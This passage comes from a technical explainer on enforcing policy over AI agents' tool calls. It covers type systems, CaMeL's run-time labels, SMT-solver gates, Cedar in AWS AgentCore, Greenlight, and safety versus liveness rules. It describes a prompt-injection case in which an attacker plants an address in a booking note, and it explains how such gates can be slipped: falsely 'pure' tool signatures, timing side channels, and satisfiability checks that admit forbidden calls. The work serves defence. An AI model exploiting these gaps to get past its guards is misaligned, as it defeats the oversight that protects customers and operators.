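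LACUNA did less well than TACIT on task performance, though the results aren't directly comparable because the tests used different models and LACUNA's ran without extended reasoning. DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0% of 392 τ²-bench tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. That 14-point gap is large, and in retail it was 22 points, though Zhao and colleagues call the overall results "on par". Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, a weaker model, solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% with ordinary tool calls. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's retail programs and 89% of Gemini's telecom programs. LACUNA seems to require more skill in Scala than TACIT does, and Zhao and colleagues suspect that models have seen too little Scala in training.

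### Enforcing types during generation

LACUNA compiles code only once it is complete. *Type-constrained generation* would instead block ill-typed code token by token, much as masking blocks calls that break a schema.

Types are harder to enforce this way than a grammar. Suppose the model has written `cancelReservation(r`. The variable `r` is a record and the function takes a string, but the program isn't wrong yet, because the model may continue with `.reservationId`. To decide whether `r` is acceptable, the engine has to track the available variables and their types, and check whether any continuation produces a string.

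LMQL, a query language from 2023, lets developers declare the type, length or form of a model's answer and steers sampling to match. Zhao and colleagues point out that LMQL constrains the output of a single model call, while LACUNA checks a whole program in its context. They propose combining the two approaches but have not done so. For example, a hole could require an integer within a given range, and a verifier could steer the model toward values that provably satisfy that condition.

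Masking could reduce the number of failed compilations, but the compiler's final check would still be needed to catch any ill-typed program that a bug in the masking engine let through.

### A typed calculus for agent configurations

Many developers describe an agent in a configuration file that names a model, a prompt, some tools and a maximum number of steps. Liu (2026), in *λ_A*, translates such files into a typed lambda calculus, a minimal formal language built from functions. A model call becomes a function from strings to strings. The agent loop becomes a *bounded fixpoint*, which follows two rules:

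$$\mathbf{fix}_0\; e\; v \to v, \qquad \mathbf{fix}_n\; e\; v \to e\,(\lambda x.\,\mathbf{fix}_{n-1}\; e\; x)\; v.$$

Here *v* is the current input and *e* is the body of the loop. In each round, the body receives the input and a function that runs the rest of the loop with one fewer step. At zero steps, the loop returns its input.

Liu proved the main theorems in Coq, a program that checks proofs mechanically. They show that a well-typed agent either produces a value of the expected type or fails at an explicit check, and that a loop with limit *n* ends within *n* rounds. The proofs assume that every call to a model or tool returns a result, so they don't cover timeouts. The translation from configuration files has only 125 tests and no proof, because these files have no formal semantics to prove it against. Liu also derives rules that flag faulty configurations and argues on paper that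 they are sound, but the list of results checked in Coq does not include this argument.

The rules look for missing branches, such as a router with no default case or a loop in which no tool ends the task. They flagged 786 of 835 public GitHub configurations (94.1%) as "structurally incomplete". This figure overstates how many agents are broken, partly because more than half of the files belong to CrewAI, whose users define tools in Python code outside the file. Liu checked 50 reported errors from other configurations by hand and found that only 27 were genuine. When the checker could also read the accompanying Python code, 96% of the errors it still reported in that sample were genuine. A refined version of the loop rule, which recognizes other ways of stopping, identified 88 configurations at real risk of looping indefinitely.

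The calculus can show that the airline's agent might never stop, but it does not track effects yet, so it can't distinguish a tool that looks up a reservation from one that cancels it.

### Labels attached to values at run time

*Information-flow control* restricts where data may go. TACIT does this with types, whereas CaMeL (2025) labels each value while the program runs, recording where the value came from and who may read it. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), one model in CaMeL writes a plan using only the user's request, and a second model, which has no tools, processes untrusted data. An interpreter runs the plan, tracks the origin of every value and checks a policy before each tool call.

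Suppose a customer asks the agent to email her itinerary, and an attacker has planted his own address in a note on the booking. If the plan takes the address from that note, the address carries a label that records its origin. The itinerary's label lists the customer as a permitted reader but not the attacker, so the interpreter refuses to send the email.

An interpreter can check the actual recipient, so it can allow the customer's address and block the attacker's. TACIT's wrapper blocks any function passed to `map` that uses the network, regardless of the recipient. But a compiler checks every branch before anything runs, whereas an interpreter finds a violation only when it reaches the offending call, after earlier calls may already have changed records.

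CaMeL also restricts the model's plans to a subset of Python without user-defined or recursive functions. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) argues that Python's dynamic types, exceptions and reflection still prevent strong guarantees about information flow. It proposes a special-purpose language with capability labels in its types, which would bring CaMeL closer to TACIT. Odersky and colleagues add that labels disappear once a value enters a model's context as ordinary text. CaMeL keeps untrusted data away from its planning model, so this loss probably matters most when a customer's next request builds on an earlier answer.

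Both Scala teams compared their systems with CaMeL's published results on AgentDojo, which now has about 950 security cases. The percentages give the share of user tasks completed:

| Model | System | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |
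| Gemini 2.5 Pro | LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
| o4-mini-high | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
| o4-mini-high | LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 |

All three systems stopped nearly every attack. TACIT's one failure is arguably a scoring error, because the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews that mentioned the attacker's hotel.

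How many tasks CaMeL completes depends heavily on the model. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* calls CaMeL's task performance "comparable", but with Gemini it completed almost no travel tasks, while TACIT completed 64.3% with the same model. With o4-mini, CaMeL beat TACIT in every domain, by 28 points in Workspace. Odersky and colleagues also describe the two systems as comparable, which is hard to reconcile with the 28-point gap. The table doesn't include an undefended agent, so it can't show how much any of the defences reduces task completion.

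### Does the guarantee follow?

The case for static types comes down to a short argument:

1. The type system is sound, so a program that it accepts has no effects beyond those in its type.
2. The compiler implements the type system correctly.
3. Every tool's signature lists all of the tool's effects.
4. Therefore, no accepted program can cause a forbidden flow.

Researchers have mechanically checked soundness proofs for the core of capture checking, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode as a whole still needs a soundness argument. The guarantee also does not cover side channels. For example, a program could run a long computation inside `map` only if the notes mention a certain illness, and anyone who timed the program would learn whether they do.

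LACUNA's implementation passed all of its roughly 400 test cases, which is encouraging but does not prove it correct. Relying on a full compiler also makes it hard to meet Anderson's requirement that the checking mechanism be small enough to analyze completely. An attacker who controls the model can keep submitting programs to look for a compiler bug.

**Truthful signatures.** The compiler checks the agent's program against the tools' signatures, but it can't check that a remote service behaves as its signature declares. Suppose the airline adds `translate(text: String): String` and declares it pure, although it sends the text to an outside company. The program `notes.map(text => translate(text))` then compiles, and running it sends the medical notes outside the airline. The type system is still sound, but any program that uses the tool can leak data this way and pass the type check.

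The function that calls TACIT's trusted model is typed as having no side effects, but the service behind the model may still retain the text, depending on how it is set up. The type system also can't check what non-Scala programs, such as `git`, do once the agent is allowed to start them.

In the AgentDojo version of TACIT, the signature of `sendEmail` may understate the function's effects. The published signature requires no capability, although the functions for reading email return classified values. According to the model's instructions, side effects inside functions passed to `map` run immediately. Unless the object that provides `sendEmail` carries a capability that the listing omits, the compiler would apparently let a program email private text to anyone by calling `sendEmail` inside `map`. TACIT's good results on AgentDojo may be due more to keeping injected instructions inside the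 wrapper, where the agent can't read them, than to the compiler's checks.

Ensuring that signatures are truthful will be hardest for third-party tools. Doshi and colleagues note that under the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools, descriptions of a tool's behavior are optional and clients should treat tools as untrusted. They propose mandatory labels for a tool's capabilities, the confidentiality of its data and the trustworthiness of its output. A mandatory label can still be false, so they suggest certification or trusted vendors for tools from an open market. CaMeL has the same problem, because whoever writes its policy has to know which tools send data out.

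An overstated signature is much less dangerous, since it only makes the compiler reject some harmless programs. The airline should therefore assume that a new tool uses the network until someone has reviewed it. It can also run tools declared pure in a sandbox with no network access, so that a tool with a false signature fails to connect instead of leaking data.

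## Checking one call against a policy

The call to cancel K7QX2M matches its schema, and a Scala version of it compiles. To refuse it, a gate has to compare the airline's rule with the facts about that reservation. Let *h* be the number of hours since the customer booked, *c* the statement that the airline has cancelled the flight, and *p* the statement that the agent may cancel the reservation. The airline's policy is then

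$$p \leftrightarrow (h \le 24 \,\lor\, c),$$

where ↔ means "if and only if" and ∨ means "or". The customer booked K7QX2M 13 days ago, so *h* is 312, and the flight is on schedule, so *c* is false. It follows that *p* is false and the gate should refuse the call.

### Three questions about a rule

That check was easy because both facts were available. When a fact is missing, the result depends on which question the gate answers:

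- *Evaluation*: does the rule's condition come out true on these facts?
- *Satisfiability*: could the rules, the facts and the permission all be true at once?
- *Entailment*: do the rules and facts guarantee the permission?

| Booked | Airline cancelled the flight? | Condition true? | Permission satisfiable? | Permission entailed? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 3 hours ago | Unknown | Yes, the first half is enough | Yes | Yes |
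| 30 hours ago | No | No | No | No |
| 30 hours ago | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| 30 hours ago | Unknown | No answer | Yes | No |

The answers differ only in the last row, where nobody has looked up the flight. Evaluation stops for lack of a value. The permission is satisfiable because the airline *might* have cancelled the flight, and it is not entailed because the airline might not have. If *R* stands for the rules, *f* for the known facts and *u* for the unknown ones, the two tests are

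$$\text{satisfiable: } \exists u, p.\; R(f,u,p) \land p \qquad\quad \text{entailed: } \forall u, p.\; R(f,u,p) \rightarrow p.$$

Satisfiability is the right test when the unknowns are choices that someone still has to make. Suppose the airline lets a customer split a fare across several gift cards. She can pay if *some* split works, and the agent can then use the split that the solver found. But a flight's status is a fact, and a gate that tests only for satisfiability would allow a cancellation because the airline might have cancelled the flight, even if it hadn't.

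### How a solver answers

An *SMT solver* is a program that decides whether some assignment of values satisfies a set of logical and arithmetic constraints. SMT stands for "satisfiability modulo theories", and the theories are subjects such as arithmetic or text strings, for which the solver has specialized procedures. Take the last row of the table and ask whether permission is satisfiable. The constraints are the airline's rule, *h* = 30, and *p*. In simplified form, the solver does this:

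1. It treats *h* = 30, *h* ≤ 24, *c* and *p* as plain true-or-false statements and ignores what they mean.
2. It looks for a combination that fits the logical structure. Making *h* ≤ 24 true and *c* false would do, since one half of the "or" is enough.
3. The arithmetic procedure checks the statements about numbers. No number is both equal to 30 and at most 24, so the solver rules out that pair and searches again.
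4. With *h* ≤ 24 false, the rule still holds if *c* is true. This combination passes the arithmetic check, so the solver answers *SAT* (satisfiable) and returns the values it found: *h* = 30, *c* true, *p* true.

If no combination is left, the answer is *UNSAT*. The solver can also run out of time or return "unknown".

The same program can test whether the rules and facts entail permission by searching for a counterexample. The gate replaces *p* with "not *p*" and runs the solver again. If the rules and facts can hold without the permission, the solver returns SAT, which means they do not guarantee it. For the booking that is 30 hours old, the solver finds the case where *c* is false. If the booking is three hours old, "not *p*" would require *h* ≤ 24 to be false, which contradicts *h* = 3. The solver then returns UNSAT, so permission follows whatever the status of the flight.

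### A solver in the agent loop

*Solver-Aided Verification of Policy Compliance in Tool-Augmented LLM Agents* (Winston, Winston and Just, 2026) puts a solver between an airline agent and its tools. The gate depends on two documents that a domain expert prepares in advance with help from a language model.

The policy encoding is written in SMT-LIB, a standard language for giving constraints to solvers. It declares a constant for each relevant fact and tool argument, such as a user ID or a timestamp. It also declares categories, such as membership tiers, and predicates for policy conditions, such as whether a cancellation is allowed. Assertions then specify how these relate.

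The other document is a *validation schema* for each tool, which is different from the JSON schemas described earlier. It lists the policy variables that the gate must fill in before checking a call to that tool, with their types and permitted values, and names the predicate that must hold. For `cancel_reservation`, that predicate would define when a cancellation is allowed. If the agent may always use a tool, its schema is empty and the gate doesn't check calls to it.

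When the agent proposes a call, the gate works in four steps:

1. It intercepts the call, along with the conversation so far.
2. A language model, GPT-4o, reads the values of the required variables out of the conversation and the arguments. This makes the gate's facts only as reliable as GPT-4o's reading.
3. The gate adds those values to the policy encoding as assertions, and adds the assertion that the tool's predicate is true.
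4. Z3, a widely used SMT solver, checks the result. On SAT the call runs. On UNSAT the gate blocks it and the agent can revise its plan, up to three times.

Winston and colleagues tested the gate on the 50 airline tasks of *τ²-Bench*, with 13 tools and a 1,242-word policy document. GPT-4.1 played both the agent and the customer, and each task ran four times. The gate reduced the share of invalid *write calls*, the calls that change the database, from about half to 29%. The agent also made somewhat fewer correct write calls, so the gate probably blocked some that it should have allowed, or the agent gave up after a refusal.

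A remaining error rate of 29% is high for a gate built on formal logic. The way errors were counted may explain part of it. Winston and colleagues measure precision and recall against the calls that each task expects, so an "invalid" call may be one that the policy permits but the customer didn't want, such as cancelling the wrong one of her two eligible reservations, which no policy check would stop. GPT-4o may also have extracted wrong values, or the encoding may have left out rules. Winston and colleagues don't divide the 29% among these causes, so their figure isn't comparable with Yu and colleagues' much lower one, which counted only breaches of encoded clauses.

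The test in the fourth step could also explain some of the errors, because the gate checks only whether permission is possible, not whether the policy guarantees it.

### How a forbidden cancellation gets through

Suppose the expert turns "customers may cancel within 24 hours of booking" into a one-way rule, and the booking is 30 hours old:

```lisp
(declare-const hours_since_booking Int)
(declare-const allowed Bool)

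(assert (=> (<= hours_since_booking 24) allowed))  ; the rule
(assert (= hours_since_booking 30))                ; the fact
(assert allowed)                                   ; the permission
(check-sat)                                        ; sat
```

The symbol `=>` means "implies". An implication is true whenever its first half is false, so the rule doesn't restrict a booking that is 30 hours old. Z3 can set `allowed` to true without a contradiction, so it returns SAT and the airline cancels the ticket. The same would happen with K7QX2M at 312 hours, or with a booking from last year.

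One of the encodings that Winston and colleagues generated automatically contained this one-way rule, and the solver allowed cancellations that the policy forbids. A human reader understands "may cancel within 24 hours" to also rule out cancelling later, but a literal translation omits that restriction.

The repair is to state both directions:

```lisp
(assert (= allowed (<= hours_since_booking 24)))
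```

The `=` operator means "if and only if" between two true-or-false values. A booking that is 30 hours old now makes `allowed` false, which contradicts the last assertion, so Z3 returns UNSAT.

But the airline also permits cancellation when it has cancelled the flight itself, so the full rule needs a second variable:

```lisp
(declare-const airline_cancelled Bool)
(assert (= allowed (or (<= hours_since_booking 24)
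                       airline_cancelled)))
```

If `airline_cancelled` has no set value, Z3 can assign it either true or false. It assigns true, since only that makes `allowed` true, and returns SAT again. The rule is now correct in both directions and the booking time is accurate, but the forbidden call runs because the flight's status never came up in the conversation.

A complete validation schema would prevent this by requiring a value for `airline_cancelled` every time. That works only if the expert remembers to list the variable and GPT-4o always has evidence for an answer. Winston and colleagues define a violation as a case where *no* assignment to the variables without a value satisfies the policy, so when a variable is unset, the check assumes a value that allows the call, if one exists.

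### Testing for entailment

The safer test has two parts, and a call should run only if it passes both:

1. The rules and facts are consistent, so the solver returns SAT for them alone.
2. Adding "not allowed" yields UNSAT.

The second part is the entailment test. With `airline_cancelled` left open and a booking 30 hours old, the solver finds a counterexample in which the flight is still on schedule, so the gate doesn't run the call. The test also handles the one-way rule "within 24 hours implies allowed". That rule doesn't prove that a 30-hour-old booking is allowed, so the gate refuses the call even though the expert forgot to state the converse.

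The first part is necessary because contradictory premises entail everything. If GPT-4o extracts both the customer's false booking time for K7QX2M and the true one from the record, the gate asserts *h* = 3 and *h* = 312. No value of *h* satisfies both, so the result is UNSAT whether the gate adds "allowed" or "not allowed". A gate that ran only the entailment test would treat the UNSAT from "not allowed" as proof that the cancellation is allowed, and would cancel the ticket.

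Rules can also contradict each other. Suppose the airline adds "no cancellation after departure" as a separate implication. A customer who books at noon for a two o'clock flight and asks to cancel at four satisfies the 24-hour rule but breaks the departure rule, so the encoding implies that the cancellation is both allowed and not allowed. The expert has to decide which rule takes priority and write that down.

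The gate can run two queries, one that adds "allowed" to the rules and facts and one that adds "not allowed". If either query is satisfiable, the rules and facts are consistent.

| Adding "allowed" | Adding "not allowed" | Meaning | Right response | A gate that tests only "allowed" |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SAT | UNSAT | Permitted | Run the call | Runs it |
| UNSAT | SAT | Forbidden | Refuse, and give the reason | Refuses it |
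| SAT | SAT | Undetermined | Hold the call, look up the missing fact, and check again | **Runs it** |
| UNSAT | UNSAT | Inconsistent | Refuse, and alert a developer | Refuses it as if the policy forbade it |
| Timeout or "unknown" on either query | | Unproven | Refuse and log it; perhaps pass the case to a person | Depends on how it treats errors |

When a call is forbidden, many solvers can return an *unsat core*, a subset of the constraints that contradict one another. For the 30-hour-old booking on a scheduled flight, the core would contain the rule, the two facts and the permission, but nothing about baggage.

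When the result is undetermined, the gate can compare the values that come with the two SAT answers. The agent may cancel in the answer where `airline_cancelled` is true but not in the one where it is false, and this identifies the fact the host has to look up. If every fact is already in place and the result is still undetermined, the rules don't cover the case and someone has to complete them.

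The host should handle an inconsistent result differently from a forbidden one because the model usually can't fix an inconsistency. If two rules contradict each other regardless of the facts, the gate will refuse every call that the encoding covers, whatever alternatives the agent tries.

### Cedar: evaluate the call, analyze the rules

If the gate has every fact it needs and the rules settle every case, evaluation, satisfiability and entailment all give the same answer. Running a solver on each call is then an indirect way to evaluate a condition. Another design evaluates each call directly and uses the solver only for questions about the rules themselves.

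Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud-computing business, sells such a gate, called Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore. AWS released a preview in December 2025 and made it generally available in March 2026, according to AWS News' *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). The agent's tool calls pass through a gateway, which checks each one against the customer's policies. The policies are written in Cedar, an open-source language that AWS developed for deciding who may do what.

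A Cedar policy either permits or forbids, and the decision for a request *x* is

$$\text{allow}(x) = \bigvee_i \text{permit}_i(x) \;\land\; \neg \bigvee_j \text{forbid}_j(x).$$

Cedar allows a call only if at least one `permit` policy matches and no `forbid` policy does. If no policy matches, Cedar denies the call. The order of the policies makes no difference.

This removes both problems with one-way rules. In Cedar, "permit if booked within 24 hours" is enough to stop a cancellation at 30 hours, because no policy permits it. The last-minute customer whose flight has already left matches both a `permit` and a `forbid`, and the `forbid` overrides the `permit`. A policy author who wants the opposite priority has to rewrite the conditions.

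Here is the airline's rule in the style of AWS's examples:

```
permit (
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"cancel_reservation",
  resource
)
when {
  context.input.hours_since_booking <= 24 ||
  context.input.airline_cancelled
};
```

The `principal` is whoever makes the request, here a logged-in user. AgentCore generates a Cedar schema from the list of tools, turning each tool into an action and each argument into a typed field. A JSON string becomes a Cedar `String`, and an integer becomes a `Long`. AgentCore rejects a policy that mentions a tool or argument that doesn't exist, so a misspelled name can't silently disable a rule.

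This schema would reject the policy above. `cancel_reservation` takes only `reservation_id` and `reason`, and AWS's *Schema constraints* says that the only context an ordinary policy can read is `context.input`, which holds the tool's own arguments. The booking time is in the airline's database. If the airline added `hours_since_booking` as an argument, the model would have to fill it in. If it used the customer's false claim, it would enter 3, and Cedar would correctly apply the rule to the wrong number.

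AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* points out that a customer's membership tier can come from a signed login token, which the model can't alter, while the quantity in an order comes from the model's call. The post also includes a rule that blocks refunds more than 90 days after the order date. The rule reads the current time from `context.system.now`, which the documentation on schemas doesn't allow. Even if the rule could read the time, the order date is one of the tool's arguments, so it would still come from the model's call.

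AgentCore also applies Cedar policies before the agent proposes a call. When the agent requests the list of tools, the gateway omits any that the policies would refuse whatever the arguments. This may reduce calls to those tools, but the gateway must still be able to refuse them. AWS argues that an agent can't try to use a tool it doesn't know about, but the telecom agents in Sankar and colleagues' study often did.

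### What a solver finds in the rules

Cedar has no loops and keeps no state between steps, so the Cedar Analysis tool can translate a policy into a logical formula and give it to a solver, which covers every possible request. The tool looks for several kinds of mistake. The examples are from AWS.

| Suspected mistake | The solver searches for | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Too broad | A request that the policy doesn't permit. There is none. | Permit a discount if the quantity is at least 100, or below 100 |
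| Too narrow | A request that the policies together allow. There is none. | Permit gold customers refunds below $100, but forbid gold and platinum customers refunds below $500 |
| Ineffective | A request that meets the condition. There is none. | Permit a refund if the customer's tier is "Gold" and also "Platinum" |
| Looser than before | A request that the new version allows and the old one refused | An order for 73 limited-edition items |

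In the last example, the old policy permitted discounts on orders of 50 or more unless they included limited-edition products. The new one says "unless they include limited-edition products and the quantity exceeds 200". The exception now applies less often, so the policy permits more. The comparison is useful here because a reader could mistake the added condition for a tightening. Cedar Analysis reports that the change makes discounts "more permissive" and leaves refunds as they were.

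Satisfiability is the right question here because the unknowns are the details of future requests, and one wrongly allowed request shows that a policy is too loose.

Whether these findings block a policy depends on a setting. AWS's post says that attaching a policy fails if the analysis detects an error. AWS's *Policy create and update* adds that the gateway's schema check always runs, but the search for overly permissive, overly restrictive and ineffective policies runs only in the mode `FAIL_ON_ANY_FINDINGS`. In that mode, the analysis covers the new policy along with all the existing ones. In the mode `IGNORE_ALL_FINDINGS`, a policy that permits everything will be accepted as long as its names and types are right.

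No setting will catch a plausible mistake. If the author types 42 hours instead of 24, the policy still permits some requests and refuses others, and it contradicts nothing, so it passes every check.

The method predates language-model agents. *Semantic-based Automated Reasoning for AWS Access Policies using SMT* (Backes, Bolignano and colleagues) describes Zelkova, which AWS built to analyze policies that control access to cloud storage and other services. Its basic operation checks whether policy *X* is no more permissive than policy *Y*, meaning that *Y* allows every request that *X* allows. This is true exactly when "*X* allows this request and *Y* doesn't" is UNSAT.

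In their example, policy *X* lets students read an exam and lets teaching assistants read both the exam and the answers. Policy *Y* lets everyone read everything in the course folder, except that students can't read the answers. *Y* allows every request that *X* allows. It also allows some that *X* doesn't, because "everyone" includes people outside the university, who can read the answers. An administrator can write a limit as a separate policy, such as "only requests from the university's network may read files", and have Zelkova check whether the real policy stays within it. The airline could do the same with a policy that permits everything except cancellations after departure.

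Backes and colleagues also describe an AWS policy whose evaluation has the problem with one-way rules. The policy was meant to accept messages from only one source, but the operator it uses makes its condition mean "*if* the request names a source, it is the approved one". A request that names no source meets this condition, so anyone can send a message. Default deny doesn't block such a request, because a `permit` matches. Zelkova detects the problem by considering requests without the source field.

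Analyzing all requests is harder than evaluating one. Wildcards in AWS's policies make the problem PSPACE-complete, which means nobody knows an algorithm that is fast in every case. Backes and colleagues found that a small change to a question could make a solver that had answered quickly run forever. Zelkova therefore runs three solvers in parallel and takes the first answer, or returns "unknown" if they time out. On a million randomly chosen questions, it answered 99% within 160 milliseconds. That is fast enough for someone editing a policy, who can also wait for the other 1%.

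### AWS Greenlight

On December 1, 2026, AWS announced Greenlight, a preview service that writes and checks rules for agents. AWS's marketing claims more than the service's mechanism supports.

Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* gives the fullest account of Greenlight, which refuses access to tools and network destinations by default. A language model drafts policies from materials that the company using Greenlight selects, such as procedures, security standards and logs of earlier tool calls. Automated reasoning then flags conflicting rules and looks for paths to resources that the agent shouldn't reach. Before accepting a policy change, the company can see which recorded calls the change would have blocked. The AgentCore gateway or Strands Box, an open-source sandbox for agents, then enforces the approved policies outside the agent.

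This looks like the AgentCore design with more help for policy authors. Le Goff's *AWS Greenlight veut empêcher un agent IA d'agir avant les vérifications obligatoires* describes the check before each action as deterministic, so the solver probably runs mostly before the agent does. The preview of blocked calls is useful because it can reveal a plausible mistake that logic alone can't. For example, a company that typed 42 instead of 24 might notice that last month's late cancellations are missing from the preview.

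Amazon's marketing makes stronger claims. Its *2026 AWS re:Invent News Brief* (2026) says that Greenlight controls agents by "mathematically proving they keep within bounds". ITWeb's *AWS creates gateway to 'trust' AI agents* reports that AWS's chief executive, Matt Garman, said in his keynote that the logic leaves "no chance of misinterpretation". That can't be true of the whole process, because before anything is proved, a language model drafts the rules from ordinary documents and can misread them.

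Garman also argued that an agent with an error rate of 0.1% per step has only about a 35% chance of getting through 1,000 steps without a mistake. That is roughly right if errors are independent (the figure is closer to 37%). A gate can prevent damage by blocking a wrong call, but it doesn't supply the right one, so the task may still go unfinished.

AWS's Shawn Bice is more careful in Computertrends' *AWS Greenlight staví matematické zábrany kolem agentů s umělou inteligencí*, where he says that the proof holds only for the policies and the system that a company has specified and modeled, and that Greenlight is one tool among several. His example of a rule for an airline is "never leave a passenger stranded." A gate can enforce part of this rule by refusing to cancel a passenger's only ticket home, but it can't make the agent find her another flight.

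AWS has a similarly named feature, Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails, which compares the text of a model's answer, not its tool calls, with a formal policy. It could catch an agent wrongly telling a customer that she has 48 hours to cancel, but not an agent wrongly cancelling her ticket.

### Solver or evaluator at run time

The two designs differ most in what happens when something goes wrong. The first two result columns are for a solver that checks each call, and the last is for Cedar in AgentCore.

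| Fault | Solver, satisfiability test | Solver, entailment test | Cedar |
|---|---|---|---|
| No rule covers the call | Runs it | Refuses | Refuses |
| The author forgot a prohibition | Runs it | Runs it if a rule guarantees permission | Runs it if a `permit` matches |
| Two rules conflict | Refuses | Refuses and can report the conflict | Refuses, since `forbid` wins |
| A fact is missing | Runs it if any value would permit it | Refuses, unless the fact makes no difference | The rule can't use facts from outside the call and the user's identity |
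| The check is too slow | Timeout | Timeout | Rare, since evaluation always ends |

Most of the danger in the solver design comes from the satisfiability test, which a developer can replace with a second query. Both designs then refuse a call when they lack grounds to permit it, though neither can compensate for a missing prohibition.

**Expressiveness.** A solver can handle rules with several unknowns, such as a rule that some split across gift cards must cover a fare. It can also determine when a missing fact doesn't affect the result. Cedar can't loop over a list, so if a rule concerns the total weight of the bags on a booking, another program has to add up the weights first. This restriction is deliberate, because it makes analyzing whole policy sets practical.

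**Speed.** AWS says Cedar evaluates policies in linear time in common cases, and Amazon claims AgentCore checks a call "in milliseconds". Z3 would probably also be quick on a single call, since most of the values are fixed and the airline's rules use only simple arithmetic. GPT-4o is almost certainly the slow part of Winston and colleagues' gate, since it has to read the conversation before every check. A solver gate that took its facts from the database would avoid that delay.

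**Size of the trusted code.** A general-purpose solver is a large program, so it fits Anderson's size requirement poorly, and a bug that made it wrongly answer UNSAT could produce a false proof that a call is permitted. An evaluator for a language without loops is much simpler. According to Computer Weekly's *AWS bets big on Lean programming language to bring mathematical guarantees*, AWS uses Lean to prove the correctness of the policy language behind AgentCore.

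Plain evaluation is the better choice for the airline's cancellation rule because a database lookup can settle both of its conditions. AgentCore's generated schema doesn't give the policy access to the result of that lookup, but Cedar is open source, so the airline could run it in its own gate. The gate could fetch the record for `reservation_id` before each check and pass the booking time and flight status to Cedar along with the model's arguments.

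## Rules about earlier calls and required later steps

Evaluating a Cedar policy, or querying a solver, settles one call on the facts at that moment. Some rules also depend on what the agent did before the call or will do after it:

- Look up a reservation before cancelling it.
- Refund a reservation at most once.
- Read a file back after writing it.

Under the first rule, a call to `cancel_reservation` can be forbidden at one moment and permitted at the next, even with the same arguments. A lookup leaves the database record unchanged, so the gate needs its own log of the agent's calls to determine whether the cancellation is allowed.

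A gate that enforces the second rule by reading only the airline's record could allow a second refund. The record will show that the airline has paid a refund, but if the first refund call times out, it may still show the old status when the agent tries again.

The agent may also have changed the record itself. *SOTERIA* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent in *τ²-Bench* whose customer wanted to cancel two reservations. The airline lets customers cancel business-class bookings, so the agent upgraded one reservation to business class and then cancelled it. Anyone who checked only the upgraded record would have seen an eligible booking. *SOTERIA* calls this a workaround that the policy does not permit. But the benchmark gave the run full credit, which suggests that its reference solution includes the upgrade.

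The third rule is harder to enforce because the required call comes later, so an agent that has just written a file has not yet broken the rule.

### Safety and liveness

A *safety property* requires that something never happens, such as canceling a reservation without looking it up first. An agent violates it at a definite step, and nothing the agent does later can undo the violation. A *liveness property* requires that something eventually happens, such as reading back every file. No finite history violates it, because the agent could still read any remaining files later.

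Let *P* be the set of runs that satisfy a property, *σ* a complete run, *u* a finite beginning of a run and *w* a continuation. Then

$$\text{safety: } \sigma \notin P \;\Rightarrow\; \exists u \text{ at the start of } \sigma \;\; \forall w:\; uw \notin P$$

$$\text{liveness: } \forall u \;\; \exists w:\; uw \in P.$$

Schneider (2000), in *Enforceable Security Policies*, studied mechanisms that watch a program's steps and stop the program when the next step would violate a policy. He proved that they can enforce only safety properties. For a gate, the argument goes like this:

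1. The gate has to decide on each call from a finite history, without knowing what the agent will do next.
2. If it refuses, it rules out every run that begins with that history and that call.
3. So the runs it allows are exactly those with no forbidden beginning, and that makes the rule it enforces a safety property.

Suppose a rule requires a read after every file write, and the agent writes a file and then stops. The gate has no call left to refuse, so it can't make the agent do the read. It could have refused the write, but that would enforce a different rule, "never write a file".

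A developer can often substitute a safety property for a required later step. One option is "after a write, the next call must read the same file", which the gate enforces by refusing every other call. Another is to treat the end of the session as an event and refuse to let the agent finish while a file it wrote is still unread. Neither makes the agent read the file, since it could keep proposing other calls until the host ends the session. If the step must happen, the host should perform it, for example by building the read into the tool that writes.

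Schneider's result covers only mechanisms that monitor a run as it happens. A program that examines the agent's plan in advance has more information, so it can also check for required later steps.

### Past-time operators

To enforce a safety rule about earlier calls, a gate needs a way to describe its log. LeanGuard, the gate that Sankar and colleagues wrote in Lean, has three *past-time operators* for this. Number the events from 1 to *n*, where event *n* is the call under review:

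| Operator | True at event *n* if | Airline example |
|---|---|---|
| PREVIOUS *p* | *n* > 1 and *p* holds at event *n* − 1 | The customer's confirmation came immediately before this call |
| ONCE *p* | *p* holds at some event *k* ≤ *n* | The agent has looked up the reservation |
| SINCE *p q* | *q* holds at some event *k* ≤ *n*, and *p* holds at every event after *k* up to *n* | The reservation has not changed since the customer confirmed |

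Each operator can have a time window, such as the last ten minutes, and a *scope*, which limits the log to events that share a user, a conversation or a resource. Without a scope, looking up any reservation would satisfy "ONCE looked up", and the agent could then cancel a different one without looking it up. When the scope is a single reservation, PREVIOUS refers to the last event that concerned that reservation, even if the agent has done other things since.

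### LeanGuard's decision

A LeanGuard policy contains *permits*, which authorize a class of calls, *requirements*, which must hold whenever they apply, and *forbids*, which block a call outright. For the rules that apply to a given call, the decision is

$$\text{allow} \iff \bigvee_{i} \text{permit}_i \;\land\; \bigwedge_{j} \text{requirement}_j \;\land\; \bigwedge_{k} \neg\,\text{forbid}_k \;\land\; \text{no evaluation error}.$$

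LeanGuard allows a call only if at least one permit applies, every requirement holds, no forbid applies, and the evaluation produces no errors. Cedar could express a requirement as a `forbid` with the opposite condition, so requirements add more convenience than expressive power. The no-errors condition matters more. Suppose the airline forbids cancelling after departure and the record has no departure time. An evaluator that treated "has departed" as false would let the call through, but LeanGuard treats the missing time as an error and refuses the call.

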